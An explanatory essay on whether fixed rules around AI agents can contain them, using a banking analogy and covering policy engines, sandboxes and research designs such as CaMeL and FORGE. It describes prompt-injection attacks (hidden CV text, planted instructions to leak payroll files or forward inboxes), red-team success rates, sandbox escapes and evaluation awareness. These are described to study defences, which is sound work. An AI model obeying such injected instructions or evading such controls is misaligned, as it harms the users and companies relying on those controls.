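# Kareem Ayoub's claim that companies can fence in AI as banks did with trading algorithms

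## What Ayoub said, and the argument in it

Kareem Ayoub is vice president of AI technical strategy at Google DeepMind, the laboratory that develops Google's AI. On 23 September 2026 he told a business audience that a company may not be able to govern an AI system fully, but that it can put a boundary of fixed rules around the system. He cited banks as a precedent, saying they did the same with their computer trading programs in the late 1980s and early 1990s. The published remark takes up a few sentences of a longer conversation. It deserves a close look because many companies now want to hand work to AI systems whose behaviour nobody can fully predict, and a boundary of this kind might let them do so safely.

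### The interview in Amsterdam

Ayoub made the remark when Tom Mackenzie of Bloomberg interviewed him on stage at HumanX, an AI conference for businesses. The technology news site The Next Web published an account the same day, *Google DeepMind’s Ayoub says companies can fence AI in, like banks did* (Constantin, 2026), which quotes some of his sentences and paraphrases the rest. No recording or second report of the conversation has been found, so his exact words are known only from those quotations.

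Constantin quotes only one sentence from Ayoub about the banks. In it, Ayoub granted that "you may not be able to fully govern the system itself", but said it was still possible to surround it with a "deterministic governance perimeter". The rest is Constantin's paraphrase, including the phrase "fixed fence" and the statement that banks put trading algorithms inside fixed rules they could check. Constantin doesn't name a bank, a trading program or a rule, so readers have to guess which episode Ayoub had in mind.

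The paraphrase is also a little stronger than the quotation. In the article's opening line, companies "cannot" fully govern AI, but Ayoub's words were "may not be able to". Constantin also presents the quoted sentence as a description of the banks' approach, so read strictly, "the system itself" means a trading program of around 1990 and "you" means a bank. Ayoub very probably meant the sentence to apply to companies and AI as well, since there is little other reason to bring up banks, but that step needs an argument.

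The setting gives some idea of which companies he meant. HumanX ran from 22 to 24 September and was the conference's first European edition, according to SiliconANGLE's *Closing the gap between your AI eyes and stomach at HumanX* (2026). By the organiser's count, it drew 3,017 people from 1,722 companies. About 67% of them were directors or more senior, and a third came from companies with at least 1,000 employees. According to the HumanX programme, Ayoub had a 25-minute slot that Wednesday titled "The Wrong Kind of Fast", presumably the interview, and a 45-minute question-and-answer session an hour later. He had used the same title in May for a talk at OMR, a marketing festival in Hamburg. The notice for that talk, OMR's *Kareem Ayoub*, is about how businesses use AI, and it describes the danger that AI works but companies only do their old tasks faster.

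So to that audience, "companies" most likely meant firms that buy and use AI, more than the few laboratories that build it. A fence that is good enough for a retailer's invoicing may be no use to a laboratory training a new model. Google also has a commercial interest in the claim, because it sells AI to firms like these, and it sponsored two events for executives at the same conference. Ayoub's HumanX speaker page, *Kareem Ayoub*, lists aligning AI development with business objectives as part of his job. These interests are a reason to look for evidence beyond his word.

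### Exponential capability, linear governance

Ayoub's remark was part of a larger worry. According to Constantin, he described the debate about AI safety as a tension between capability, which grows exponentially, and governance, which grows only linearly. A quantity grows exponentially when it multiplies by the same factor in every period, and linearly when it gains the same amount. Suppose both start at 1, capability doubles every year and governance gains 1 a year. After five years capability is at 32 and governance at 6; after ten years, they are at 1,024 and 11. The contrast is a figure of speech, since nobody has a common unit for the two. The idea behind it is that if people have to study each new system before they can govern it, they fall further behind every year.

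Against that background a perimeter looks attractive, because its rules can govern what a system does regardless of how it works. A rule that no large payment goes out without a signature does not need rewriting when a more capable model arrives, but it may not hold as well against that model. Ayoub's own business advice makes this problem pressing. He told companies not to bet against model progress, and said the best of them ask whether their product would become ten times better if the model underneath it did. A company that follows this advice will keep putting stronger models inside the same fence, including models that did not exist when it drew up the rules.

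Ayoub divided the problem into three questions: what role AI should play in research and development, how transparent AI systems must be, and who controls them. The perimeter offers some transparency, since a company can inspect its rules even where it cannot understand the model. It mostly replaces the question of who controls the system with the question of who writes the rules. It seems unable to settle how much research a laboratory should hand over to AI, because somebody has to make that choice before there is any rule to enforce.

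He said Google's Frontier Safety Framework, the company's policy on dangerous capabilities, is also part of the answer. Mackenzie brought up two further proposals. Dario Amodei, the head of the rival laboratory Anthropic, wants to pace the development of the most capable models. Demis Hassabis has called for a regulator led by the AI industry and, in another borrowing from finance, modelled on FINRA, which oversees brokerage firms in the United States. *Google DeepMind CEO Demis Hassabis calls for creation of AI standards body* (Deutscher, 2026) reported that call in July, when Hassabis was still Google DeepMind's chief executive. By the time of the interview, *Behind the exit of DeepMind’s CEO* (Nolan, 2026) had described low morale and delayed models at the laboratory, and in Amsterdam Ayoub was asked about morale too. On regulation, he replied that guardrails will need partnerships beyond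 technology companies.

In the reported remarks, Ayoub comes closest to practical instruction when he discusses sandboxes, which are closed computing environments that limit what a program inside them can reach. He said that the best companies he works with build safe sandboxes quickly instead of waiting for multi-year IT projects. He was recommending speed at least as much as safety, and Constantin does not report him connecting the advice with the banks. Still, a sandbox is a perimeter, and the only specific kind he is reported to mention. He also said that companies fail when they reward staff for hiding their AI use. This matters for any fence because an employee who pastes customer records into a private chatbot account is using AI outside it.

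### Models, agents and deterministic rules

An AI model is a program whose behaviour comes from training. Engineers run it on a huge number of examples while an automatic procedure adjusts its internal numbers, often billions of them, until its outputs fit. Nobody writes down the steps it takes from a question to an answer. The familiar chatbots run on language models, which produce text a fragment at a time, usually with some chance involved in each choice. Someone who asks a chatbot twice for a polite letter to a landlord about a broken boiler may therefore get two different letters. Both may be perfectly good, and they have no effect until a person sends one.

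An agent can send the letter itself. Constantin defines an agent as a model with memory, tools and internet access, which let it work through long, multi-step tasks. Suppose someone asks an agent to book a train from Amsterdam to Paris on Friday for under €100. The model proposes a first action, such as searching the timetable. Ordinary software around the model runs the search and feeds back the result, and the model then proposes the next action. This repeats until the agent has bought the ticket and charged it to someone's card.

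Ayoub said that the product shifted from the model to the agent around the end of 2025, and that the strongest returns so far are in software engineering. He described a gap between frontier uses of AI, such as speeding up drug discovery, translating ancient texts and helping detect gravitational waves, and its use in most businesses, where the focus is often on drafting or summarising email. Agents are the main reason a company needs a perimeter. If a company uses AI only to draft email, the employee who reads the draft already acts as a checkpoint.

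A deterministic rule gives the same result every time for the same input. If a cash machine has a daily limit of €500 and a customer who has already withdrawn €400 asks for another €200, the machine refuses, whatever the customer's reason. The bank can therefore test the rule before installing the machine, by trying totals of €490, €500 and €510, and know how the machine will treat each of them from then on. The bank would learn much less from a similar trial of a language model, since the model may answer the same question differently tomorrow, and a small change to the question may change the answer greatly.

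A deterministic rule gives the same answer to the same request under the same limit, though the limit itself can change. If the bank raises it to €600 on Monday, the rule is still deterministic. By contrast, if a company permanently required a second AI model to approve every payment, the rule would be fixed, but the model's verdicts on the same request could still vary from one day to the next. Ayoub's word, "deterministic", is stricter than "fixed" on the point that matters here, whether a company can know the outcome in advance.

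A rule can also be perfectly reliable and still not prevent the mistake that matters. A cap of €100 per purchase will always stop the train-booking agent from buying a €300 first-class ticket, but it will allow an €80 ticket to Brussels even if the user asked to go somewhere else.

### The argument, step by step

Written out in full, the argument from the banks goes like this:

1. A company cannot fully govern an AI system from within.
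2. A company can build fixed rules around the system.
3. Banks did this with trading algorithms in the late 1980s and early 1990s.
4. It worked.
5. AI agents are like those trading algorithms in the respects that matter.

Therefore, companies can contain AI.

Ayoub stated (1) and (2) in quoted remarks, though he qualified (1) with "may". (3) comes from Constantin's paraphrase of him. The reported remarks include neither (4) nor (5), and without them the history of banking does not support the conclusion.

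Premise (1) explains why a company would want a perimeter. A company that cannot train a system to behave and then confirm that it always will has to rely heavily on the perimeter, which would otherwise be an extra precaution. But the premise gives no reason to think that a perimeter can be relied on that much. Someone could accept (1) and conclude that companies should keep such systems away from anything important.

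Premise (2) is close to trivial on one reading, since anybody can write a rule. The conclusion requires rules that are harder to write, because they must prevent the harms a company cares about and still let the agent do enough to be worth having. Cutting an agent off from every tool and network would certainly contain it, but would also remove most of its value to the company.

The banks are the example of companies that supposedly managed both. For the example to support the argument, their rules must have worked, which could mean that the software refused the orders it was written to refuse, that the bank escaped ruinous losses, or that the market as a whole came through unharmed. One of these can happen without the others. If every bank's program sells on the same afternoon, each within its own limit, prices may collapse even though every limit held. Anyone who reasons from the banks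 to AI has to say which kind of success they are claiming and show that the banks had it.

The argument probably depends most on premise (5). An analogy supports a conclusion only to the extent that the two cases share the features that produced the result. Trading algorithms and AI agents are both software that companies run to make a profit, but that similarity does not help the argument much. It would help if both had the features that allow rules to work: every action passes through a point where a rule can stop it, the owner can list the harmful actions beforehand, and the program does not search for ways around the rules.

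Claim (1) faces a difficulty. The analogy is close only if the banks, too, were unable to govern their systems from within. Yet computer trading in that period largely meant programs that followed preset rules, which their owners could read. By contrast, the Systemic Risk Centre (2025), a research centre at the London School of Economics, wrote that banks generally cannot explain how AI works or how it makes decisions. If the banks of 1990 understood the programs they were fencing in, some of their success (supposing they had it) may have come from that understanding rather than from the fence.

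Ayoub may have mentioned banks only to show a room of executives what he meant by a perimeter, not as proof. In that case (3), (4) and (5) drop out, and the claim depends on what rules around an AI agent can do today. The conclusion also becomes narrower. It says only that a company can make sure certain listed actions, such as a purchase above €100, never take effect. A promise to "contain AI" is much broader, because it means that nothing seriously harmful gets out by any route, including routes nobody thought to list. The headline suggests this broader promise when it says companies can fence AI in "like banks did", but Ayoub's quoted sentence commits him only to the narrower one.

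## Why a company cannot fully govern an AI model from within

Governing an AI model from within means relying on a trained model's judgement to keep its behaviour acceptable. A developer does this by training the model to refuse certain requests, and a company that buys the model does it by writing instructions such as "ask a manager before paying a new supplier". Either can also add a guard model, a second AI model that judges the first one's inputs, plans or outputs. Although the guard model is a separate program, using one still counts as governing from within because its judgement is also learned. This definition excludes policy engines, which are ordinary software that applies fixed rules, such as refusing every payment above €500, regardless of a model's judgement.

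Ayoub's first premise was that a company may be unable to govern a system fully by such means. The year before, Google security specialists Díaz, Kern and Olive (2025) had put it more bluntly in *Google’s Approach for Secure AI Agents*, writing of the "practical impossibility" of guaranteeing that an agent's actions will match its user's intent under every threat.

### What training leaves to chance

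A language model computes a probability for each possible next fragment of text, and the software around it usually draws one at random, so its replies depend partly on chance. Training changes the probabilities. If training cut the chance that an AI agent handling refunds approves a fraudulent claim from 20% to 0.1%, the agent would still approve about ten out of 10,000 fraudulent claims.

A company can switch off the random draw so that the software always takes the most likely fragment. This makes the model more repeatable, but the company still doesn't know what it will do with a claim worded in a way nobody has tried. Engineers cannot tell from the model's internal numbers how it will extend its training examples to new cases. This is probably a more serious problem than the randomness, because customers can word a claim in endless ways and a company can test only some of them.

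Such mistakes can happen without an attacker. Díaz and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to "email Mike about the project update". If the agent picks the wrong Mike from the address book, it may send confidential plans to a stranger.

### Instructions and data in one stream of text

The software around a model combines the company's written instructions with everything the model reads while it works, such as emails, invoices and web pages, into one long text prompt. In a prompt injection attack, somebody hides instructions in that material, and the model follows them as if its user had given them. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 article for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C describes a recruiter who asks a model to score CVs, one of which contains hidden text telling the model to approve that candidate for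 interview.

Older software had a similar flaw. In SQL injection, an attacker types a database command into a field on a web page, such as the surname box, and the database runs it. Engineers learned to prevent this by passing whatever the visitor types to the database in a separate slot, whose contents it never treats as a command. David C argues that a language model has no such slot, because it predicts the next fragment of text from all the text so far, and at that level instructions and data are no different.

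Developers do try to teach models to tell instructions from data. They train a model to rank its user's instructions above anything it finds in a document, or they put markers around the document to show that it is data. These methods lower the rate of successful attacks, but the model still has to make the distinction each time, and sometimes it will fail. David C thinks there is a good chance that nobody will ever fix prompt injection the way engineers fixed SQL injection. Díaz and colleagues make a similar point only about current designs, so a future kind of model might have a real partition between instructions and data.

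### Errors over many steps

An agent calls its model many times during a task, so small error rates add up. If it gets each step right with probability *p*, and the steps are independent, its chance of completing *n* steps without an error is *p*ⁿ. At 99.5% reliability per step, its chance of completing 200 steps without an error is 0.995²⁰⁰, or about 37%, so it will make at least one error in about 63% of such tasks. To complete 99% of them without an error, it would need to be right about 99.995% of the time, or wrong roughly once in 20,000 steps.

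This estimate is too pessimistic in one respect, because it counts all slips as failures even though agents often notice and repair them. If the agent repairs nine errors out of ten, the rate of lasting errors falls to 0.05% per step, and its chance of finishing without one rises to about 90%.

The assumption of independence is also doubtful. An agent that misreads a supplier's name at step 3 may carry out the remaining 197 steps correctly but for the wrong supplier. Díaz and colleagues point out that flawed logic or a hidden instruction can enter at every round of planning, and that an instruction stored in the agent's memory can affect later, unrelated tasks. In *Emerging Security Practices for AI Agents* (2026), the Frontier Model Forum, an industry body for developers of the most capable models, lists compounding errors, alongside prompt injection, among the reasons agents take consequential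 actions that nobody intended.

### How often attacks succeed

The security firm Gray Swan has measured how well current models resist prompt injection. Its benchmark uses attacks that members of the public devised in competitions, one of which Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026) analysed. The version behind the results below has 37 scenarios, in which an agent writes code, uses tools or operates a computer through its screen. Gray Swan selected 1,804 attacks that worked well across different models. These attacks are designed to cause irreversible harm, such as leaking private data or making a payment the user never asked for.

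Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 reports the results. An attacker had a 0.1% chance of success against Fable 5.1 with one attempt and a 1.0% chance with fifteen. For most models from other companies, the chance over fifteen attempts was between 24% and 53%, though it was 9.2% for the best of them, Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash. Anthropic has made fast progress. On an older Gray Swan benchmark, an attacker with ten attempts had a 33.6% chance against Claude Opus 4.5, according to The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*. On the current benchmark, the chance over ten attempts against Fable 5.1 is 0.7%. The improvement is clear, although the comparison is rough because the two benchmarks contain different attacks.

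However, a fixed list of attacks can make a model look safer than it is. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection* reported that when Anthropic released Claude Opus 5, fifteen attempts had a 2.0% chance of success against it. By September, the figure for the same model was 4.8%. Anthropic's report then covered nine more scenarios and 670 more attacks, which probably account for most of the rise.

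A second test used an attacker that adapts. Gray Swan trained an automated attacker on 40 coding scenarios against earlier Claude models, then gave it 200 attempts per scenario against newer ones. It ran the test with and without what Anthropic calls probes, which inspect incoming material for hidden instructions before the model acts on it, and so do the work of a guard model. Anthropic gives these figures for models that reasoned at length before acting:

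| Model | Attempts that succeeded, no guard | Attempts that succeeded, with guard | Scenarios breached, no guard | Scenarios breached, with guard |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 9.26% | 2.05% | 31 of 40 | 18 of 40 |
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.68% | 0.39% | 27 of 40 | 11 of 40 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 0.30% | 0.09% | 7 of 40 | 5 of 40 |

With Fable 5.1, the guard cut successful attempts by nearly four fifths, yet the attacker still got through at least once in 18 of the 40 scenarios. If all the scenarios had been equally vulnerable, 200 attempts on each at a 2.05% success rate would have breached about 39 of them. Some tasks are therefore fairly safe while others are much more vulnerable, and a company can't easily know in advance which kind its own task is.

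Obedience also did not improve consistently with each release. Fable 5.1 did better than Opus 5 against the fixed list but worse against the adaptive attacker. For an earlier model, Opus 4.8, VentureBeat gives 7.03% without safeguards and 2.09% with them against an attacker from the same tool. These figures are close to those for Fable 5.1, so they show little of the progress that the fixed benchmarks suggest. The conditions favoured the attacker, which had practised on the same scenarios used in the test. Anthropic notes that real attackers usually can't do that, and that repeated attempts make them easier to detect.

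The best result for guard models comes from web browsing. Across 129 scenarios, the attack success rate against Opus 5 was 3.7% without extra defences and zero with two of them, according to The Decoder. One defence scans what the model reads and the other blocks dangerous actions, so an attack has to beat both. Zero out of 129 is impressive, but it is still compatible with a true success rate of up to about 2.3% (at 95% confidence), and that bound assumes future attacks will resemble the ones in the test.

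Both defences are trained classifiers. Díaz and colleagues say guard models can catch subtle or changing patterns that fixed rules miss, but warn that new kinds of attack can fool them in ways that are hard to predict. They consider such defences inadequate on their own for critical or irreversible actions. The Frontier Model Forum also advises companies not to rely on detection alone.

### The case for training values and judgement

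Some developers would say this underestimates control from within. They regard training a model to have good values and use judgement as the main safeguard, because no list of rules can foresee every case. A price cap cannot stop an agent from booking a cheap ticket to the wrong city, but a model that understands where the traveller wants to go would not book it. Díaz and colleagues, who favour fixed rules as a first layer, concede the general point. Sending an email after reading a document may be what the user asked for, or it may leak the document, and the two are hard to distinguish with a simple rule.

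Anthropic's published constitution for Claude is the best-known statement of this approach. It describes the values the company wants its models to have and lists a few absolute prohibitions. Beyond those, it mostly gives reasons and leaves the model to judge how to apply them. That judgement may be the only safeguard against a harm that nobody thought to forbid.

There is evidence that such training works. Anthropic found that Claude Sonnet 5 followed the constitution better than its predecessor, Sonnet 4.6, and took fewer risky actions on its own initiative. Kovacs (2026), in *Anthropic Rolls Out Mythos 5.2 With Improved Bug Hunting, Fewer Sandbox Escapes*, reported that the November model Claude Mythos 5.2 was less likely to leave its closed environment in controlled tests. If better training is the reason, the improvement did not require a new rule for each way of escaping.

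The improvement has been uneven. Mythos 5.1, the same model as Fable 5.1 with looser safeguards, was less likely than earlier models to ignore explicit constraints, but did slightly worse than Opus 5 on misaligned behaviour overall. Anthropic also raised its estimate of the risk of catastrophic harm from misalignment from "very low" to "low", citing uncertainty after recent incidents in security tests. It later tested Opus 5.5 as an agent without the extra safeguards it uses in its products. The model refused malicious requests less often than any other in the comparison, according to Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Opus 5.5.

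Under its constitution, Claude should behave consistently "whether or not you think you’re being tested or observed", a line quoted in *Anthropic should measure the effect of evaluation awareness* (cheema, 2026). Models now often suspect that they are being tested, which makes tests of their behaviour weaker evidence. *How AI systems are becoming harder to monitor* (2026), by the UK's AI Security Institute (AISI), discusses the wider problem.

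Values and judgement can therefore do something that rules cannot, but nobody has shown that they do it every time. Anthropic itself also puts classifiers around its models instead of relying on values and judgement alone.

### How much the premise establishes

The premise is sound for today's models. AISI states that developers cannot yet guarantee that their systems will always behave as intended, and Google's specialists agree, even though Google would benefit from being able to guarantee this. The "cannot" in Constantin's opening line therefore fits the evidence better than Ayoub's more cautious "may not be able to".

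However, a company that cannot fully govern a model may still be able to govern much of what it does. If an agent read 10,000 invoices a month and ten of them contained hidden instructions to pay a fraudster, it would make about one fraudulent payment every eight years at the 0.1% rate that Gray Swan measured for a single attempt against Fable 5.1. Many finance departments would welcome that record. But if one determined fraudster practised on a similar agent and then sent 200 invoices, about four would succeed at the 2.05% rate from the adaptive coding test, even with a guard in place. Neither rate comes from an invoicing system, so these figures only illustrate how much the risk depends on who is attacking.

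How much a firm can leave to a model also depends on the damage a failure would do. A firm that can reverse a wrong payment the same afternoon might reasonably let a well-trained model handle small invoices. It would be reckless to trust the model with a €5 million transfer that the firm could never recover, or with the only copy of its customer records. David C advises that a language model may be the wrong tool if a system cannot tolerate the remaining risk.

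## How fixed rules around an AI agent work

As in the train-booking example, an agent's model only requests actions, and ordinary software carries them out. Programmers call each request a tool call. It specifies a tool, such as "purchase", and details such as the shop, the item and the price. Ayoub's second premise, that a company can build fixed rules around an AI system, relies on this arrangement. The company can decide in advance which requests its software will carry out, even though it can't determine what the model will request.

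### From a proposed action to its effect

Suppose an agent that orders office supplies tries to buy a chair for $240. In the design that Díaz and colleagues describe, a policy engine intercepts the request before it reaches the shop and checks it against rules that people wrote in advance. The rules can depend on the action itself, such as whether it involves money or can be undone, and on earlier events, such as whether the agent has just read material from an untrusted source. The engine then allows the action, blocks it or asks the user to confirm it.

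Google gave the example of a spending limit in May 2025. The engine blocks any purchase over $500 and asks the user about purchases between $100 and $500. It would therefore ask the user about the $240 chair, allow a $60 keyboard without asking, and block a $700 desk.

Asking a person for approval makes the outcome less predictable. The engine will request approval for every $240 purchase, but two users may answer differently, and a user who gets forty such requests a day will probably stop reading them. *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows*, a blog post from Amazon's cloud-computing division, AWS, calls this approval fatigue and advises against relying on human approval as the main control.

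The engine also needs reliable facts about each action, since a tool's name may not make clear what the tool does. Chuvakin (2025), in *How Google secures AI Agents*, explains that Google's engines use action manifests, which record what each action does and what kinds of data it handles. In Chuvakin's example, a user asks an agent to set up a virtual machine, but a prompt injection leads the agent to ask to delete all databases. The engine identifies the deletion from the manifest and blocks it.

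Some of the facts a rule checks come from the model itself. In an AWS example, a rule allows a bulk discount only if the customer has platinum status and orders at least 50 items. The customer's status comes from a login token that the model cannot alter, but the quantity comes from the model's request. That is safe enough if the shop's software then uses the quantity that the engine checked. Relying on the model for a price is riskier, because a cap on the requested price doesn't help if an agent requests a $90 purchase and the shop charges $900. A careful company would take the price from the shop or also put a limit on the payment card.

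AWS sells a policy engine that sits in a gateway between the agent and its tools. AWS argues that the rules belong there because nobody can trust the model to enforce its own limits, and checks scattered through dozens of tools are hard to audit. The gateway blocks everything by default, and each rule allows an exception. It also hides from the model any tool that the rules would always block.

### Six purchases of $90

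Google's spending limit, taken literally, covers one purchase at a time. If the agent buys six $90 keyboards in separate orders, each order is below $100, so the engine allows them all without asking anyone. The user has spent $540, an amount the engine would have blocked as a single order. This can happen even when the agent isn't trying to evade the rule, for instance when it buys equipment for six new employees one by one.

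The repair is to keep a running total. In the pseudocode below, "committed" is the money already promised to earlier purchases, and it starts at zero:

```
when the agent requests a purchase of "amount":
    if committed + amount > 500:
        block
    committed = committed + amount        (reserve the money)
    if amount >= 100 and the user says no:
        committed = committed - amount    (release it again)
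        block
    allow
```

The first five keyboards bring the total to $450. The sixth would bring it to $540, so the engine blocks it. The agent can still spend $450 without asking anyone. A company could prevent this by applying the $100 approval threshold to the running total too, but the user would then have to approve the second through fifth keyboards.

The engine must reserve the money before the order goes out, because agents often make several requests at once. InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026) gives an example with a $5,000 cap and three simultaneous transfers of $2,000. If the rule counts only completed transfers, the total is still zero when all three requests arrive, so the engine approves them all and $6,000 leaves the account. If the rule counts requested transfers, the engine refuses the third.

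Somebody also has to decide when the total resets to zero. If it resets at midnight, an agent could spend $500 at 11:55 p.m. and another $500 ten minutes later. A rolling 24-hour window, the longest that AWS's product supports, prevents this. However, according to the product's documentation, *Temporal policies*, each session has its own total, and the program that calls the gateway chooses the session's identifier. An agent that can open sessions can therefore renew its own budget, so the company should have software outside the agent's control open them.

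A rule with a running total is still deterministic as long as its input includes the record of past purchases. It takes more work to test, because the company has to try sequences of requests as well as single ones. The company must also store the record securely, because anyone who can edit it can change the rule's decisions. AWS's older rule language, Cedar, covers single requests, and a program can prove things about a set of Cedar rules. InfoQ reports that AWS put rules about past actions in a separate language, Dogwood, because that analysis does not work for them.

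### Anderson's three requirements

Computer scientists worked out what makes such a checkpoint trustworthy long before there were AI agents. In 1972 the US Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and worried that a legitimate user might write a program to get at secret files. Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, proposed a reference monitor, which checks every attempt by a program to use data, a device or another program against a list of what its user may do. The mechanism has to meet three requirements:

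1. It must be tamper-proof, since a program that can alter the check can remove it.
2. The system must always invoke it. If some program can skip the check, that program becomes part of the security mechanism and has to meet the same standard.
3. It must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely. Otherwise nobody can know that it works in every case.

Anderson showed how Honeywell's GCOS III, a commercial system of the time, failed to meet these requirements. The hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory. But to read or write a file, the program had to call the operating system, which mostly ran with that check switched off, so the second requirement failed. If the operating system is itself counted as the checking mechanism, it failed the third requirement, because it and its supporting software contained 200,000 to 300,000 instructions.

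The same questions apply to a policy engine. In *Scan the Skill, Govern the Action*, Taneja and Weber (2026) describe a product of their company, Pheo, that checks an agent's commands on the computer where the agent runs. They concede that an agent able to run commands there could edit the configuration file that turns the check on. The product signs its records, so a company could later detect changes to them, but this would not stop the agent from disabling the check. An engine on a separate machine where the agent has no account comes much closer to meeting the first requirement.

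A guard model cannot meet the third requirement, because nobody can completely analyse its billions of learned numbers. A policy engine can realistically meet it, at least in the part that compares requests with rules. Anderson's panel also warned that adding protection afterwards has little chance of making a system secure. For an AI agent, that warning applies to the software around the model. If the agent already has the company's card number and an open internet connection, it can pay a shop directly, and a policy engine added later to the official purchasing tool will not stop it.

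### Least privilege with Progent

Under the principle of least privilege, a program should have only the permissions its job requires. Díaz and colleagues argue that an agent's permissions should also change with the task, so that it can't delete files while helping someone write a story. No company can write a separate rule list for every request an employee might make. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) therefore uses a language model to write the list and a deterministic program to limit what that model can change.

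A Progent rule names a tool, sets conditions on its arguments, and either allows or forbids calls that match. Progent applies the rules that forbid calls first, and it blocks any call that no rule covers. When it blocks a call, it can stop the agent, ask the user, or return an error message so that the agent can try something else. A company can also add permanent rules, and rules written for one task cannot override what the permanent rules forbid.

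Suppose a user asks an agent to do whatever a certain email says. The first list allows only a search for that email. The email turns out to contain a request to post a summary of recent messages to the user's account on Slack, a workplace chat service. The model that writes the rules now proposes allowing three more tools, for reading email, looking up the user's Slack name and posting to Slack. Once the agent has looked up the name, the model proposes restricting posts to that one account.

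Progent treats these two proposals differently. Let A(P) be the set of all tool calls that the list P allows. A new list P′ takes effect automatically only if

A(P′) ⊆ A(P),

that is, if every call it allows was already allowed. To check this, Progent uses a solver, a program that searches for a call that P′ would allow and P would not. If no such call exists, as with the restriction to one Slack account, permissions have only shrunk. The three extra tools fail the test, so they need approval. Now suppose one of the recent messages contains a hidden instruction to forward the whole inbox to a stranger. The message may fool the model into proposing a rule that allows outgoing email, but that proposal also fails the test and has to wait for approval.

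The guarantee is that permissions never grow without approval, so much depends on who approves. The legitimate request for Slack and the malicious request for outgoing email both come from text the agent has read, and the solver can't tell them apart. Shi and colleagues let a company refuse all expansions, accept them all or send them to a person. The approval step adds no protection if the company accepts them all, but the agent in this example can't finish its task if the company refuses them all. Sending them to a person seems best for anything valuable, and it need not be much work, since only 6% of rule changes needed approval in one of their tests.

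### Where data came from and where it may go

A list of permitted tools is not enough to ensure that each email is safe to send, because the same tool can send a public brochure or a payroll file. Debenedetti and colleagues from Google DeepMind and elsewhere published a design called CaMeL in 2025 that addresses this by keeping untrusted text away from the model that makes the plan. *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes how the design works and extends it.

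CaMeL uses two language models. A privileged model receives the user's request and writes a plan in a restricted form of the programming language Python. It does not read the emails or documents involved. A quarantined model reads those, but it cannot give the privileged model instructions. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the plan and calls the tools. If a user asks an agent to send the quarterly report to a client whose address is in the meeting notes, the plan might look like this:

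```
notes   = read_file("meeting notes")
address = ask_quarantined_model("What is the client's address?", notes)
report  = read_file("quarterly report")
send_email(to = address, attachment = report)
```

Suppose an attacker hides an instruction in the notes to send the payroll file instead. The quarantined model may follow it, but whatever the model outputs becomes the value of "address". The plan has no step that opens the payroll file, and nothing in the notes can add one.

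The attacker can still replace the client's address with another, and the plan would then send the report to the wrong person. CaMeL therefore tags every value with its sources and who may read it. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy that checks the tags. If the report's tag lists the company's staff and the client as permitted readers, a policy can block sending it to anyone else.

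The tags have no effect unless a policy uses them. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) works through a similar email program in which the recipient's address comes from an untrusted message. The address keeps its "untrusted" label through to the sending step, but the example's policy requires only the subject and body to be trustworthy, so it allows the address.

CaMeL's strict separation makes some tasks awkward. If the request is "do whatever this email says", the privileged model cannot write the full plan, because the steps are in the email, which it is not allowed to read. Progent can handle that request, but only by asking someone to approve the new permissions.

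*Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues, 2026) presents FORGE, a system that lets agents plan as they like. It is also built for several agents working at once and messaging each other. FORGE records every message, tool call and result as a point in a graph, with an arrow from each event to any later event it may have influenced. When an agent proposes an action, FORGE follows the arrows back to the earlier events that may have influenced it and applies its rules to all of them.

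FORGE's rules are in Datalog, a language for querying databases. One rule blocks an action if it sends something outside the organisation and depends on both untrusted input and sensitive data. Datalog allows a definition to refer to itself, so an event can be defined as tainted if it is untrusted input or depends on a tainted event. The taint therefore passes through any number of steps, including messages from one agent to another. Suppose an agent reads a supplier's document with a hidden instruction, opens a confidential file and then tries to email an outsider. FORGE blocks the email because it depends on both the document and the file.

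FORGE checks each action in the following order:

1. It identifies the message that led to the action and waits until the graph contains everything that message may depend on.
2. It collects the facts about the action, the identity of whoever is responsible for it and the relevant part of the graph.
3. It derives everything that follows from the rules. If any rule denies the action, FORGE blocks it, even if another rule allows it. If no rule applies, it uses a default that the company has chosen.

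To be safe, FORGE assumes that each new message from a model depends on every earlier message in the model's history. Once an agent has read both the supplier's document and the confidential file, this rule would stop it from sending an outsider even a harmless email to confirm a meeting. CaMeL tracks individual values, so it could let that email through. Palumbo and colleagues make clear that FORGE's guarantee holds only if every relevant action passes through the monitor before it takes effect, which is Anderson's second requirement, and if the recorded facts match what happened.

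### Sandboxes and agents that run code

These designs work best when an agent acts through a known set of tools. But a programming agent usually has a terminal, where it can run any command. A single command may start a script that opens hundreds of files and contacts a website, and the command's name may not show this.

The traditional way to restrict an agent is a sandbox. The operating system gives the agent's programs access to certain folders and network addresses and blocks everything else, whatever command the agent runs. This is simple but crude. As Palumbo and colleagues point out, a sandbox that forbids all external email also blocks the external emails the agent is supposed to send.

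A sandbox is probably most useful combined with a policy engine. AWS's gateway, for example, governs only the requests that pass through it, so an agent that can run a script with open internet access can bypass it. A sandbox prevents this if its only outgoing connection leads to the gateway. It also helps to keep passwords outside the sandbox. FORGE can add a password to a web request after approving it, so the agent never needs the password.

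*Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026), from Google DeepMind and several partners, combines a sandbox with rules that take account of past actions. It runs each command in a throwaway layer on top of the real files and records the command's system calls, the requests a program makes to the operating system when it opens a file or a network connection. It also holds back any outgoing message. If the rules permit everything the command did, Tether makes the changes permanent and releases the message. Otherwise it discards both.

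Tether also keeps a security label on every file. In its main example, a file called servers.csv holds a company's inventory and has the label "sensitive", while report.txt is "public". The agent runs three commands:

1. It uploads report.txt to an outside website. Tether allows this, since the file is public.
2. It copies servers.csv over report.txt. Tether allows this too, but report.txt now has the label "sensitive".
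3. It uploads report.txt again. Tether blocks the upload.

The first and third commands are identical, so a rule based only on a command's text would have to treat them the same way. Tether can tell them apart because the label stays with the data, even if the agent first copies the inventory through ten temporary files.

The calculation behind this is short. With the labels in the order public < internal < sensitive < secret, and leaving out some details, Tether updates them as follows:

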